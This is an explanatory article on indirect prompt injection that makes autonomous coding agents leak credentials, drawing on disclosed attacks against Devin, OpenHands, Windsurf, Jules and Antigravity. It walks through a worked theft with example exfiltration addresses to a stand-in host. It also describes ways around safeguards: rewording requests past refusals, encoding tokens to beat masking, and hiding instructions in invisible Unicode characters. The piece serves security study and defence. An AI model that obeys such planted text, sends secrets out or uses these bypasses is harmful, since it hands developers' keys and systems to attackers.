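# Prompt injection that leaks credentials from autonomous coding agents

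## How a coding agent can be made to leak a credential

A coding agent is a language model that reads, writes and runs code through tools, often with little supervision. A developer gives it a task in ordinary language, such as fixing a bug, and the agent works through files, web pages and error messages to complete it. The agent usually holds credentials such as passwords, keys or access tokens, which are strings that let whoever holds them act on an account. An attacker who can place text where the agent will read it can sometimes make the agent send those credentials out. Security researchers call this method indirect prompt injection, and they call the theft itself exfiltration, which means sending data to someone who should not have it.

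The model acts on the computer only by writing requests for tools. A surrounding program carries out each request and returns the result to the model as more text. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who has attacked about a dozen of these products, describes the cycle in Ethiack's *Agentic Problems and the Rise of Zombie AIs* as perceive, reason, decide, act. The usual tools are a shell, which runs commands on the machine, a browser or simpler way to fetch web pages, and functions for reading and editing files. The chat window also counts as a tool, and an important one, because many chat windows display images as well as text.

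A coding agent needs a token for GitHub, the code-hosting site, to fetch a private project or propose a change to it, and a cloud key to run tests that depend on a database in the company's cloud account. Developers commonly supply both as environment variables, which are named values that the operating system passes to the programs it starts. This keeps the credentials out of the code, but almost any command the agent runs can print them. Rehberger showed in *How Devin AI Can Leak Your Secrets via Multiple Means*, on his blog Embrace The Red, that the agent Devin has a built-in store for secrets and exposes each entry as an environment variable while it works.

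### Why the model follows a stranger's text

Prompt injection exploits the mixing of trusted instructions and untrusted data in a single prompt, which lets whoever controls the data override the instructions. Rehberger (2024), in *Trust No AI*, credits the firm Preamble with discovering it and reporting it privately to OpenAI in May 2022, and the programmer Simon Willison with naming it. In the indirect form, the attacker puts the instructions in something the model will read, such as a web page, a source file or a GitHub issue (a bug report that almost anyone can file on a public project), and the model follows them as if the user had given them.

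Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a web form and a poorly written program runs them. Developers can reliably prevent SQL injection by passing the command and the data to the database separately. Language models don't have this separation. As Willison (2025) wrote in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, everything "gets glued together into a sequence of tokens", so the model has to work out from the text itself which instructions to follow.

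Vendors wrap each stretch of text in tags that name its role, such as the user's request, the model's own reasoning or the output of a tool, and they train the model to treat tool output as information it should never obey. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) tested whether models internally represent text according to those tags. Ye and colleagues trained classifiers on models' internal activations, using identical text under different tags so that the classifiers could learn only the effect of the tags. When they tagged an entire conversation as user text, the passages written in the style of the model's reasoning still registered as reasoning, at 85%, and barely as user text, at 2%. Writing style had a stronger effect than the tags on how the model represented those passages.

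The same team tested credential theft by having an agent with a shell and a local file of secrets summarise a web page that hid an instruction to upload the file. When the instruction was a plain fake user command, it succeeded 0 to 2% of the time on every model except the small gpt-oss-20b, where it reached 26%. When the page added forged reasoning in the model's own style, success rose to between 56 and 70%. These were OpenAI models of the GPT-5 generation and slightly older, so the percentages are weak evidence about the models of late 2026. The gap between the two attacks is more informative, because it shows that a model can resist familiar injections almost perfectly and still fail against an unfamiliar phrasing. This would be expected if the model has learned to recognise attacks rather than where text comes from.

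Newer models resist injections much better. Willison (2026) recorded an Anthropic-commissioned test in which none of 720 injections succeeded, but weeks later he recorded a different kind of attack by Rehberger with a reported success rate of 80%. Planted text can also work without looking like an instruction. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) describes GitHub comments that imitate the format in which software delivers comments to the model, so that part of a stranger's comment looks like a separate comment from a project maintainer. This worked on Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI.

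### The lethal trifecta and the AI Kill Chain

If nobody can guarantee that the model will ignore planted text, the harm that text can do depends on the agent's capabilities. Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for three that are dangerous in combination: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to send data out. A coding agent can easily have all three, with tokens in its environment, strangers' bug reports to read, and an open internet connection. Removing any one of them prevents this kind of theft, but an agent without credentials cannot deliver its work, and an agent that reads nothing from outside cannot investigate much. Willison considers the ability to send data out by far the easiest of the three to restrict, and noted that chatbot vendors had usually fixed such leaks by removing it.

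Rehberger's term, the AI Kill Chain, describes the order of events. In Embrace The Red's *AI Kill Chain in Action* he lists three steps:

1. Prompt injection: planted text reaches the model and steers it.
2. Confused deputy: the agent uses its own authority on behalf of someone who has none. The attacker has no right to read the token, but the agent does.
3. Automatic tool invocation: the tool runs without a person approving it.

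The chain covers more than stolen credentials, because the tool at the end could just as well install malware or delete files. (*Promptware kill chain* is a different term. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (2026) uses it for a seven-stage model of prompt injection as a way of delivering malware.)

Willison (2025), in *The Summer of Johann*, stressed the word "automatic" because many products try to break the chain at that step by asking the user to confirm each action. Confirmation works only if people read what they confirm. Anthropic inserted one clearly dangerous command into the sessions of 1,053 paid testers, and 13.6% refused it. The company was arguing for its own automated alternative at the time, but the refusal rate is low enough that confirmation prompts would still look ineffective even if the result were considerably biased.

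### One theft, step by step

Suppose a developer's agent has a GitHub token in its environment, with the invented value `demo-token-4821`.

1. A stranger files an issue on the developer's public project. The first half reports a believable crash. Further down, a supposed debugging step asks whoever investigates to look up a certain setting and open a "diagnostics" page with the value in its address.
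2. The developer asks the agent to look into the newest issue and turns to other work.
3. The agent fetches the issue. Its text joins the developer's request in the same stream, and the model takes the debugging step for part of the task.
4. The agent runs a command that prints the environment variable, so the token is now in the text the model is working with.
5. The agent requests the address `collector.example/page?v=demo-token-4821`.
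6. The attacker's server logs the request, as web servers ordinarily do, with the time and the full address. The attacker opens the log and copies the token.

The attack works even if the diagnostics page doesn't exist, because the request has already carried the token out by the time an error comes back. The agent only has to look something up on the web, which coding agents do routinely; it doesn't have to send a file or write an email. The attack is also zero-click, meaning that the user doesn't have to click or approve anything once the agent has read the planted text. Rehberger carried out this kind of theft against Devin in April 2025, starting from a planted GitHub issue.

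Even if a vendor removes the agent's browser and blocks the shell's internet access, the token can still leave through the chat window. Chat programs commonly format replies with Markdown, a notation in which a writer includes a picture by giving its address. When the agent's reply contains such an address, the chat window automatically fetches the picture. If the planted text gets the agent to "illustrate" its answer with a picture at `collector.example/p.png?v=demo-token-4821`, the same line appears in the attacker's log as before. The user sees a broken image or nothing. Because the request comes from the program that displays the chat, which may be the user's own browser, it doesn't pass through a firewall around the agent's machine.

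Rehberger had reported this leak through image loading in eleven products by the end of 2024, among them ChatGPT, Claude, Google Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat. Embrace The Red's *OpenHands and the Lethal Trifecta* recommends a well-known fix, a content security policy that limits which domains the chat window may load images from. The policy fails if an attacker can collect data through a domain it allows. In January 2026 Willison described a leak of private emails from Superhuman AI, an email assistant whose policy allowed images from a Google domain. Google Forms runs on that domain and stores whatever data arrives in a request, so the attacker could collect the emails with an ordinary online form.

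A link can also leak a credential contained in its address. Slack, Discord and Teams fetch a linked page to build a preview, which sends the address out without a click. An ordinary link is less effective because the user has to click it, although an attacker can make the stolen part of the address invisible on screen. A domain-name lookup, the step by which a computer finds the server behind a name, can also carry a secret, as was demonstrated with both Claude Code and Amazon Q Developer.

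### Vendor's machine or developer's machine

What a thief gains depends on where the agent runs. In his conference slides *Agentic ProbLLMs*, Rehberger (2025) classifies Devin, OpenHands, Google Jules and the web version of OpenAI's Codex as cloud agents. He classifies Claude Code, GitHub Copilot, Cursor, Windsurf and Amazon Q Developer as local agents, which run on the developer's own computer.

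A cloud agent's machine holds roughly what the user has given it: the project's code, stored secrets, and tokens for connected services such as Slack. An attacker who steals one of these credentials can use it from anywhere until someone revokes it. Rehberger warned in Embrace The Red's *I Spent $500 To Test Devin AI For Prompt Injection* that an attacker could use the keys on such a machine to reach an organisation's other computers and its cloud infrastructure, and he advised users not to connect the machine to a company network without fully understanding the risk. Cloud agents also tend to work unsupervised. For example, a user can assign Devin a job in a Slack message and not check on it until it reports back.

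An attacker can steal far more from a developer's own computer. Unless the agent is confined, it can open whatever the developer's account can open. According to lecture slides from UT Austin, this may include the SSH keys that log in to servers, API tokens, files of secrets, email and unreleased source code. The slides also note that checkpoints, which let a developer undo an agent's edits, cannot undo the sending of a key. If the planted text gets the agent to run the attacker's program, the attacker may control the developer's whole working environment.

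Local agents more often ask for permission before they act, which offers some protection. To limit how often they ask, vendors give them an allow-list of commands or internet domains they may use without asking. Attackers look for an allowed command or domain that can do more than the vendor realised, or they get the agent to edit its own settings so that it stops asking.

### The Month of AI Bugs

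Rehberger found many of these weaknesses by testing one product after another. He works independently and previously set up several offensive security teams, which attack systems to find their flaws. In August 2025 he published the results almost daily as the Month of AI Bugs. According to Embrace The Red's *The Month of AI Bugs* (2025), the series aimed to raise awareness of the risks, press unresponsive vendors to act, and shorten the time the industry takes to fix such flaws.

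Embrace The Red's closing index, *Wrap Up*, lists 29 posts. Four are about Windsurf, three each are about Devin, Google Jules, Amazon Q Developer and Amp Code, and two are about OpenHands. The last post presents AgentHopper, an experimental virus that uses coding agents to spread between code repositories.

Rehberger followed responsible disclosure, which means telling the vendor privately first and publishing after a fix or a set period. When vendors did not fix the problem, he waited at least 90 days, and often more than 120, before publishing. He reported the Devin flaws, for example, in early April.

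His paper *Agentic ProbLLMs*, published on 25 February 2026, draws the series together. It reports more than two dozen previously unknown vulnerabilities and describes their recurring pattern, the AI Kill Chain. The paper attributes the vulnerabilities to design choices by vendors, who relied on the model's output as a security control, isolated the agent poorly and in some places left out human approval. It also warns of a "normalization of deviance", the sociologist Diane Vaughan's term for an organisation getting used to breaking its own safety rules because nothing has gone wrong yet.

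The series proves that a leak was possible but gives little idea of how often an ordinary attacker would succeed, because one skilled person chose the targets and kept working on each until an attack worked. Even a low success rate may be enough to steal a credential, since an attacker can plant the same text in many places and needs it to work only once.

Vendors' responses ranged from fixes within weeks to no reply. Willison, reviewing the first half of the month, thought that fixing most of the remaining flaws would have made the products much less useful.

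## Devin and OpenHands

The makers of Devin and OpenHands were among the slowest to respond. Rehberger reported credential leaks to both companies in March and April 2025, and neither had fixed them when he published his findings that August.

Cognition presents Devin as the first AI software engineer. Devin works on a virtual machine with its own shell and browser. OpenHands, from All-Hands AI, was originally called OpenDevin. People can run it on the company's cloud service or on their own computer inside a container, an isolated environment with its own files and programs.

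### How Devin's secrets became environment variables

To give Devin access to a database, a user enters a name and a password on a settings page. According to Cognition's January 2025 help page *Session-Specific Secrets*, an application could then read the secret "like a normal ENV variable" if the session started after the user saved it.

Planted text therefore only had to get the agent to list its environment variables, without naming a secret or locating the store. Cognition encrypted the secrets on its disks, but a running session needed them in readable form.

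### The ways out of Devin

Rehberger paid $500 for 30 days of access to Devin. He began by searching its system prompt, which contains the vendor's standing instructions to the model and descriptions of its tools, for tools that could contact the outside world. He quickly identified the shell and the browser.

To leak data through the shell, Rehberger planted instructions in a GitHub issue about a runtime error and asked Devin to investigate the latest open issue. Devin's first attempts to send the data failed, but it fixed the errors, as coding agents are meant to do, and sent the environment variables to his server. Rehberger reported on Embrace The Red that the network didn't block the transfer because Devin's machine had unrestricted internet access by default.

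Devin also leaked the variables through its browser. It listed them, wrote a short Python script to encode them for a URL, and opened the attacker's page with the data attached. In a variation, Devin pasted Jira and Slack tokens into a third-party website. Rehberger had earlier used that technique on Operator, OpenAI's browsing agent, and OpenAI added a mitigation after he reported it.

Devin's chat window also loaded images from any domain, so an attacker could leak the variables through an image's URL. In this test, Devin read the planted instructions on a website it visited. The model sometimes refused overly direct requests for a secret but complied with a vaguer one.

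A more unusual route was a tool named `expose_port`. A port is a numbered connection point on a computer, and programs listening on Devin's ports normally can't be reached from the internet. The tool gives such a program a public web address so that a user can try out a website Devin is building. Its description included an instruction for the model to make sure that exposed apps don't access local backends, but Rehberger observed no firewall rule or similar control enforcing this.

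In this attack, planted text got Devin to start a web server offering the machine's files, open it to the internet, and send its address to the attacker through an image. Unlike in the other attacks, the attacker could then fetch the files directly, so they didn't all have to fit into one request. Rehberger reported on Embrace The Red that Devin refused at first, but complied once he split the steps across two web pages so that each looked less suspicious.

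Slack was the one place where an automatic leak failed. Rehberger had Devin post a link containing a secret there, expecting Slack to leak it by fetching a preview. Slack never requested the link, so he concluded that Cognition must have disabled previews for Devin's messages. It is unclear whether the company did this for security or to keep threads tidy.

The link still worked. Devin had written a short program to put the secret into the address as characters that the screen doesn't display, so the link looked harmless. When Rehberger clicked it, his browser encoded the invisible characters and sent them with the rest of the address. This attack is weaker than the others because it needs someone to click the link, but even a careful person could be fooled. Microsoft had already fixed the same problem in its Copilot assistant.

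An attacker can also take control of the whole machine. In another test, which Rehberger published on Embrace The Red, a GitHub issue mentioned a support tool on an outside website. Devin followed the link, downloaded a program and tried to run it. The operating system denied permission, so Devin changed the file's permissions and ran it again, which gave Rehberger remote control. In early attempts Devin had stopped the program fairly quickly, so Rehberger set his server to send its commands as soon as a connection opened, which is enough to take the secrets within milliseconds. The secrets may therefore already be stolen when an agent notices its mistake and cancels the command, and the user still has to replace every credential on the machine.

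### OpenHands: a refusal and a mask

OpenHands had the same image flaw, and Rehberger used it to take the `GITHUB_TOKEN`, the agent's access token for GitHub. He put instructions on a web page. OpenHands read the page, looked up the token and leaked it through an image address without the user clicking anything.

Two defences initially blocked this attack. First, the model refused to fetch the token and send it to a stranger's server. Rehberger reworded the request so that it no longer plainly asked for a token, but OpenHands then detected that the value was a secret and hid it in the output. He bypassed this by having the agent change the form of the token before displaying it.

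Neither defence is a security boundary, meaning a limit that holds whatever the attacker does. A refusal depends on how the model reads a text, and the attacker wrote part of that text. Anyone can also install OpenHands, try different wordings in private, and plant only the one that works. Devin's refusals gave way in the same manner, and the experiments by Ye and colleagues showed how much a change of style alone can affect the success rate. Refusals do stop crude attempts, and better models refuse more of them, but this doesn't justify leaving a valuable token within the agent's reach.

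Masking hides known strings in the output an agent displays. An agent that can run programs can bypass it by encoding a secret in a different form, which the attacker can then decode. To catch every such encoding, the filter would have to recognize every reversible transformation a program can perform. A shell command can also read a secret and send it off without displaying it.

Masking is still useful against accidental leaks, such as a key that turns up in a log or a shared transcript. According to the release notes in Cognition's *2026* (2026), since October 2026 Devin has masked each line of a saved private key separately, so that the key stays hidden when a command prints only part of it. This change addresses partial copies of a key but not transformed ones.

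Rehberger published a second OpenHands attack a day after the first. Embrace The Red's *ZombAI Exploit with OpenHands* describes a takeover like the one on Devin. The user asked the agent only to visit a web page, but it also downloaded malware and ran it. Rehberger reused a demonstration he had built for Anthropic's computer-use agent and changed only the program it downloaded. He also tried a version of ClickFix, a scam in which a web page persuades visitors to copy a command and run it. OpenHands copied the commands into its terminal on the first attempt.

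All-Hands AI advises people who run OpenHands locally to keep it in its container. The container limits a takeover to the code, data and secrets inside it, which helps considerably on a personal computer full of other files. It does not prevent the image leak, which bypasses the container.

### What the companies did with the reports

Rehberger reported the Devin flaws to Cognition on 6 April 2025, and the company acknowledged the report a few days later. He then asked several times about the status and the timeline for fixes. He published his findings after more than 120 days without an answer.

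Rehberger reported the flaw to All-Hands AI first, on 13 March, through the private reporting channel on the project's GitHub page. He wrote again a week later and got no response. On 30 March he opened a public ticket complaining that nobody was assessing security reports, and someone confirmed there that the project would look at his. He had hoped to present the flaw and its fix in a conference keynote the next day, but he took it out of the talk because no fix existed. His further messages in June and July got no reply.

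All-Hands AI responded on 9 August, the day Johann Rehberger published his post about the token leak on Embrace The Red. He wrote that the timing may have been a coincidence or the result of an email he had sent through another channel the day before. He ended the post by hoping for improvements, but it is unclear whether the company later stopped the chat window from loading outside images.

The two companies seem to have had different problems. All-Hands AI seems not to have read the report until Rehberger complained in public, which a small project could fix by assigning someone to read its security inbox. Cognition confirmed receipt within days and then stopped answering, so its silence is harder to explain as a missed message. Neither record shows what the engineers were doing in the meantime.

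### The proposed fixes and Devin in late 2026

Rehberger sent Cognition a list of recommendations with his report. The most important was to block outbound connections by default and let users open the ones they need. This would stop the shell and browser leaks unless the attacker could receive data through a permitted site. But coding work constantly draws on online software packages, documentation and other people's bug reports, so someone would have to list the permitted sites in advance or keep approving new ones. An agent that needs a blocked site at night may have to wait until morning for approval.

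Cognition's *Security profiles* describes sets of restrictions that administrators can now attach to Devin's sessions, including an allow-list of internet destinations. The list applies to shell commands, browsing, package installation and scripts. If Devin needs a site that isn't on the list, it requests access, which a user can grant for that session. If an administrator makes a profile mandatory, users can't approve access beyond its limits. Another setting removes the token for GitHub's command-line program from the machine, but Devin can still work with the code through a separate connection.

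The profiles became generally available on 7 August 2026, sixteen months after Rehberger's report. They are optional, and each restricts only what the administrator configures, so a session without a network policy still has open internet access. Customers who run Devin's sessions on their own machines must enforce the network list themselves.

A coding agent can block network access by default, at least when it runs on the developer's computer. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the default sandbox in local versions of Codex keeps network access off until the user enables it. Cognition labels internet domain filtering in the local version of Devin "currently unstable".

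Rehberger's second proposal was to stop the chat window from displaying images and links that lead to untrusted domains. This fix would inconvenience users the least. They would lose some externally hosted diagrams and screenshots, or have to click to see them, and would have to copy some links by hand. A network allow-list on Devin's machine can't replace this fix, since image requests can bypass that machine.

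On 11 November 2026 Cognition added a profile option called "Ask before loading external content". In sessions with this option, images from other sites load only after a click. The wording implies that they still load automatically in other sessions, nineteen months after the report. Requiring a click offers little protection if the user cannot tell that an image address contains a secret, as Rehberger's Slack link showed.

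Since July 2026, Devin's web chat has shown links in Devin's replies as preview cards. Similar previews in Slack did not leak data, but the new cards could if the software fetches an attacker's page to build them. The release notes don't specify how it builds the cards, and nobody has demonstrated a leak through them.

The third proposal was to require approval outside the chat for sensitive actions such as opening a port. If the model requests approval in the conversation, planted text can influence the request or lead the model to act as if the user had already approved. A separate confirmation, in which ordinary software shows the user the actual command, doesn't depend on the model's account of what it is doing. Devin's main attraction is that a user can assign a job in Slack and leave, and this proposal weakens it because the job may stop at every approval.

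Devin now has several such approvals, most of them optional. Administrators can block individual tools of connected outside services or set them to "Needs approval". Stored secrets have a "Require approval before each use" switch, which is off by default according to Cognition's *Giving Devin Credentials*. In the local version, users can choose a mode in which a fast model judges most actions and runs those it considers, in Cognition's words, "clearly safe". This spares the user many interruptions, but it again makes a model's judgement the safeguard, which Rehberger had advised against.

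The port tool's current status is less clear. In February 2026 Cognition extended its Secure mode, which removes Devin's "native internet deployment capabilities", to customers without an enterprise contract. The release note doesn't mention `expose_port`. Notes from August still refer to exposed ports in the preview toolbar, so Devin can still expose ports in some form.

Rehberger also wanted Cognition to warn customers that an attacker could take any secret on Devin's machine, and that they should not connect the machine to a company network. He suggested installing protective software on it and adding a monitor that would intervene when Devin browsed to untrusted sites or downloaded programs. OpenAI had added such a monitor to Operator, and Rehberger recommended one to All-Hands AI as well, though he acknowledged that it wasn't a complete solution. A monitor would interrupt some legitimate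 work and could miss an attack that looked like ordinary work.

Perhaps the most useful change is that, according to Cognition's November 2026 documentation, Devin now supplies each secret only to the commands and tools that need it, instead of exporting secrets into every shell. Listing the environment variables, the first step in several of Rehberger's attacks, should therefore reveal much less. But Devin still decides which commands receive a secret. Planted text could presumably still get the database password attached to a command by convincing Devin that the command needs it, unless the user has turned on approval for that secret.

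Cognition also recommends giving Devin its own account on each service, which limits what an attacker can do with a stolen password. Since July 2026, Devin has been able to log in to cloud services with short-lived identity tokens, so a stolen token soon stops working.

Cognition's release notes, *2025* (2025) and its 2026 successor, contain no entry about the reported flaws from September 2025 to mid-November 2026, so they don't confirm a fix. The new controls don't confirm one either, since they may be a response to Rehberger or to requests from large customers. Cognition may have told those customers more, because it releases security documents through its *Trust Center* on request to people who sign a non-disclosure agreement. It moved all enterprise customers to a new version of Devin by December 2025 and has since adopted much newer models, so the exact texts that worked in April 2025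 may well fail now. But the conditions that made them dangerous, open internet access and automatically loaded images, appear to remain unless an administrator changes the settings.

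## Windsurf, Google Jules and Google Antigravity

Windsurf is a code editor with a built-in agent that runs on the developer's computer with the developer's permissions. Google paid about $2.4 billion for a non-exclusive licence to its code, and in November 2025 released Antigravity, an editor based on that code. Google also makes Jules, a cloud agent that works much like Devin. Rehberger reported flaws in Windsurf and Jules in May 2025, and six months later he found the Windsurf flaws again in Antigravity.

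### How a comment in a source file leaks a key

Many projects keep their keys in a plain text file named `.env`, from which programs load them as environment variables. The file is usually in the project folder, where a coding agent constantly reads files. To steal the keys, an attacker can write instructions to the agent in a comment, a note in a source file that the computer ignores when it runs the code. The comment might arrive in a downloaded library or a stranger's contribution to the project.

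When the developer asks Windsurf to explain the file, the model reads the comment along with the code and follows the comment's instructions. The agent opens `.env` with its file-reading tool and puts the contents into a URL on the attacker's server. It then either requests that URL with `read_url_content`, a tool for reading web pages, or displays it as an image in the chat. Windsurf doesn't ask the user to approve any of these steps. According to Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded!*, both leaks have been known since at least May 2025.

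By default, Windsurf requires the user's approval before it runs a terminal command. But this attack doesn't need the terminal, because the agent has separate tools for reading files and fetching pages.

### Memories and connected tools

A planted instruction can also keep working after the session ends. *Windsurf Agent Security Risks*, a product profile by the security vendor Adversa AI, reports that Windsurf's agent can save "memories", notes that it loads in later sessions, without approval. An attacker can therefore get the agent to save an instruction to leak data through images. Later sessions will load the instruction and leak data again even if the developer has deleted the file it came from, so the developer has to find and delete the memory as well. Windsurf keeps automatic memories separately for each workspace (the project folder open in the editor), which should confine the repeated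 leak to one project.

Rehberger calls this attack SpAIware. He first demonstrated it in 2024 on ChatGPT's Mac app, where a planted memory made ChatGPT send the attacker everything the user typed and every reply, including in future chats. OpenAI had fixed the app by the time he published *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*.

Windsurf users can also connect the agent to outside services through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of giving a model more tools. In Embrace The Red's *Windsurf MCP Integration*, Rehberger connected Slack and asked the agent to review a file with a planted comment. The agent fetched the latest message from a private team channel and posted it to a public one. It didn't ask for approval first, and Windsurf had no setting to require it.

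This leak doesn't involve an attacker's server, so a network allow-list that includes Slack wouldn't stop it. Rehberger wanted users to be able to choose whether each tool runs automatically, requires approval or stays off. Windsurf let users turn off individual tools, but turning off the Slack tool for protection also kept the agent from posting to Slack when they wanted it to.

Rehberger sent Windsurf this report on 30 May 2025. The company acknowledged it a few days later and then stopped answering, much as Cognition did over Devin. After he began publishing his Windsurf findings in August, the company's chief executive contacted him and said it was now working on fixes.

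### Independent findings in October 2025

Two security firms independently found similar leaks. Tenable's *Windsurf Prompt Injection via Filename* describes a test on Windsurf 1.10.7 in which a file's name contained an instruction for any AI assistant to read the file and follow what it said. Windsurf added file names to the user's prompt, so the attack worked without the developer opening or mentioning the file. When the tester asked for help getting started with the project, the agent followed the instructions and sent information to an outside website through `read_url_content`.

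HiddenLayer's *Data Exfiltration from Tool-Assisted Setup* (2025) covers version 1.12.12 and older. The firm hid instructions in a project's README. The agent followed them, searching the project for keys and sending out a test key it found in `.env`. This worked even with automatic execution switched off.

HiddenLayer and Tenable scored the severity of these leaks differently on CVSS, a standard scale from 0 to 10. HiddenLayer gave its finding 7.5. Tenable's *CVE-2025-36730* (2025) lists 4.6 for its own finding, or 3.5 on an older version of the scale. Tenable rated the attack as local, dependent on the user's actions and minor in what it reveals, while HiddenLayer assumed a remote attack that needs no user action and reveals a lot. The higher score seems more accurate for a developer with a working cloud key in `.env`.

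HiddenLayer was also credited with a more serious flaw, published on the same day. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-62353* (2025), an entry in the vulnerability database of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, describes how planted text could make Windsurf read and write files outside the current project. Adversa AI lists the flaw's severity score as 9.8. An attacker could use the flaw to reach the developer's SSH keys as well as the keys in the current project.

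Windsurf never answered HiddenLayer, which wrote on 1 August and again two weeks later. OX Security also got no reply to an October report about flaws in the editor's browser code. Windsurf did reply to Tenable, saying on 18 August that the bug was in its priority queue, and on 5 September that it was still thinking through a solution and believed some existing protections helped. Tenable suggested requiring approval for `read_url_content`. It wrote twice more in October, apparently without an answer, and published on 14 October with no fix available.

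### Does trusting the workspace help?

Windsurf was referring to Workspace Trust, a protection in VS Code, the Microsoft editor on which Windsurf is built. When a user opens a new folder, a dialog asks whether they trust whoever wrote the files in it. If they answer no, Windsurf turns off the AI chat, so the attack can't start.

This helps a developer who only wants to read an unfamiliar project. It does little for anyone who wants to use the agent, because, as Tenable objected, an AI coding assistant stops being one without its AI features. The security firm Mindgard made the same objection to Antigravity's version of the dialog. In ordinary VS Code, people who decline can still do most of their work, so declining is a realistic option.

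The dialog also covers only part of what the agent reads. A developer may rightly trust a project written by colleagues, then ask the agent to read a stranger's web page or bug report. A trusted project can also take in a poisoned file from outside later. Because the user answers before the agent has done anything, the dialog can't show which file the agent will read or where it will send the contents. Tenable's proposal would show the user the address just before the request goes out. However, it would also interrupt every routine documentation lookup online, and some users would soon approve requests without reading them.

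### Windsurf becomes Devin Desktop

Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-33069 · Codeium · Windsurf* (2026) describes another flaw, which became public in April 2026. Without any action by the user, web content controlled by an attacker could make Windsurf version 1.9544.26 connect to a malicious MCP server, which could then run commands on the computer. The flaw has a severity score of 8.0.

Windsurf is now called Devin Desktop. Journal du Net's *Test de Devin Desktop (ex Windsurf)* (2026) reported in June that Cognition had acquired Windsurf and merged it with Devin. By August, the old website redirected permanently to Devin Desktop, according to DevTools Review's *Windsurf Is Now Devin Desktop* (2026).

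Adversa AI's profile, which includes the April 2026 flaw, gives the most recent account of the default settings. Terminal commands need approval, but the page reader and the memory tool don't, and the chat window loads images from any domain. If that is still correct, the leaks Rehberger reported in May 2025 remain possible in a default installation. But the profile uses the old product name and relies partly on tests from 2025, so Cognition may have changed some of these defaults in Devin Desktop. It is also unclear which of the fixes the chief executive promised were released.

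### Jules and its open internet connection

Jules runs on a virtual machine in Google's cloud so, as with Devin, an attacker who hijacks it gets what the user has given it but not the user's personal files.

Rehberger published three posts about Jules on consecutive days in August 2025. As Willison summarised them, the first showed that Jules leaked data through images and through `view_text_website`, a tool that fetches the text of a web page. The second showed an attacker taking remote control of Jules's machine, which had unrestricted outbound internet access. Any program on the machine could send data out, so Google couldn't stop the theft just by fixing the image display and the web page tool.

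Strangers can easily get Jules to read their text. According to Google's *Changelog* (2025), adding the label "jules" to a GitHub issue starts a task. A stranger can write an issue that looks reasonable enough for a maintainer to add the label. Since 8 August 2025, Jules has also searched the web without being asked, so it may read pages that nobody on the project chose.

### Instructions that people cannot see

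Rehberger's third post, *Google Jules is Vulnerable To Invisible Prompt Injection*, showed that a maintainer who carefully reads an issue before assigning it to Jules may still miss instructions hidden in it. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, includes Tag characters, which correspond to ordinary letters and punctuation but are invisible on screen. A language model still receives these characters as part of the text and can often read them as if they were normal letters.

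In the visible text of his test issue, Rehberger asked for a harmless comment in the program's main function. In the invisible text, he asked Jules to add another function, then compile and run the program. Jules drew up a plan, which was approved automatically, and carried out all of it. The added function only printed a message, but an attacker could use the same method to ask for secrets.

On the day he published, Rehberger repeated the test with the label. Jules copied the whole issue, including the invisible characters, and its interface didn't display them either. The additional function appeared in the plan once he expanded the individual steps. Users can therefore catch such an attack by reading the plan closely, but only if they wait for the plan and know what they asked for.

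Rehberger had reported the underlying weakness in Gemini, Google's family of models, on 22 February 2024, and Google accepted it as a valid bug. The weakness became more dangerous as the models improved, and Gemini 2.5, released in 2025, frequently followed invisible instructions. Rehberger reported its effect on Jules on 26 May 2025, a week after the product launched. At Google's request, he shared his posts a week before publishing them, but he had heard nothing about a fix by the time they came out.

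This problem is much easier to fix than other prompt injection because ordinary software can delete Tag characters before the model sees them, and source code and bug reports almost never need them. The main dispute is over who should do the filtering. Many models follow invisible instructions, including Anthropic's Claude, and Rehberger wrote in *Amazon Q Developer for VS Code Vulnerable to Invisible Prompt Injection* that, to his knowledge, Anthropic didn't intend to change this. That leaves the filtering to the makers of each application. Amp Code, another coding agent, had been fixed by the time Embrace The Red covered it that August. Google makes both Gemini and Jules, so it could have filtered the characters in either place. Filtering wouldn't stop visible instructions, but a reviewer could notice those.

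Google's changelog for Jules lists no fix for any of these flaws up to 22 August 2025. It does list a new "critic" that reviews each proposed code change. The critic might catch a planted function, but it might not catch a leak, since sending a key to a website doesn't change the code. It is unclear whether Jules still loads outside images and has open internet access by default in late 2026.

### Antigravity and the flaws it inherited

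About a week after Antigravity's release, Rehberger tested whether Google had fixed the problems he had reported to Windsurf, and found that it had not. He planted instructions in a source file, and when he asked the agent to explain the file, it sent him the contents of `.env` through an image. The agent's tool for reading web pages, still named `read_url_content`, also leaked them. As in Windsurf, tools connected through MCP ran without approval, and users had no way to require it.

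Antigravity also followed invisible instructions, a weakness that came from Gemini. This weakness and the one inherited from the licensed code made each other worse. In one demonstration, Rehberger put invisible text in a ticket on Linear, a service for tracking work. The agent fetched the ticket through MCP and ran the attacker's commands on the developer's computer.

It is unclear whether Windsurf told Google about Rehberger's private reports when it licensed the code. Google could have read about the flaws anyway, because his Windsurf posts had been public for about three months when Antigravity came out. Rehberger guessed that the launch caught Google's security team a bit off guard.

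*Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, by the security firm PromptArmor, describes an attack that bypasses one of Antigravity's default protections. An attacker hides instructions in one-point type in an online guide to accounting software, and a developer gives the guide to the agent. The agent then looks for cloud credentials in `.env`. By default, Antigravity's file reader refuses to open files listed in `.gitignore`, which names files to keep out of the shared code. That list includes `.env`, so the agent prints the file with a terminal command instead.

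The agent then opened the attacker's address in Antigravity's browser. Google's default allow-list for the browser included webhook.site, a service where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it. The agent didn't have to ask the user first, because the recommended settings let Gemini decide when a command or a plan needs human review. This attack required the optional browser tools, but PromptArmor found three other leaks that didn't.

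Willison (2025) recommended giving coding agents only credentials for non-production accounts with strict spending limits. This limits what a thief can do with stolen credentials, whether or not the vendor fixes the vulnerability, but it doesn't prevent the theft.

### Known issues and intended behaviour

Google warned users about data exfiltration when they first opened Antigravity. Its public page of known issues included data exfiltration and command execution through prompt injection. Google was working on fixes, according to the page, but reports of these problems were not eligible for rewards from its bug bounty programme.

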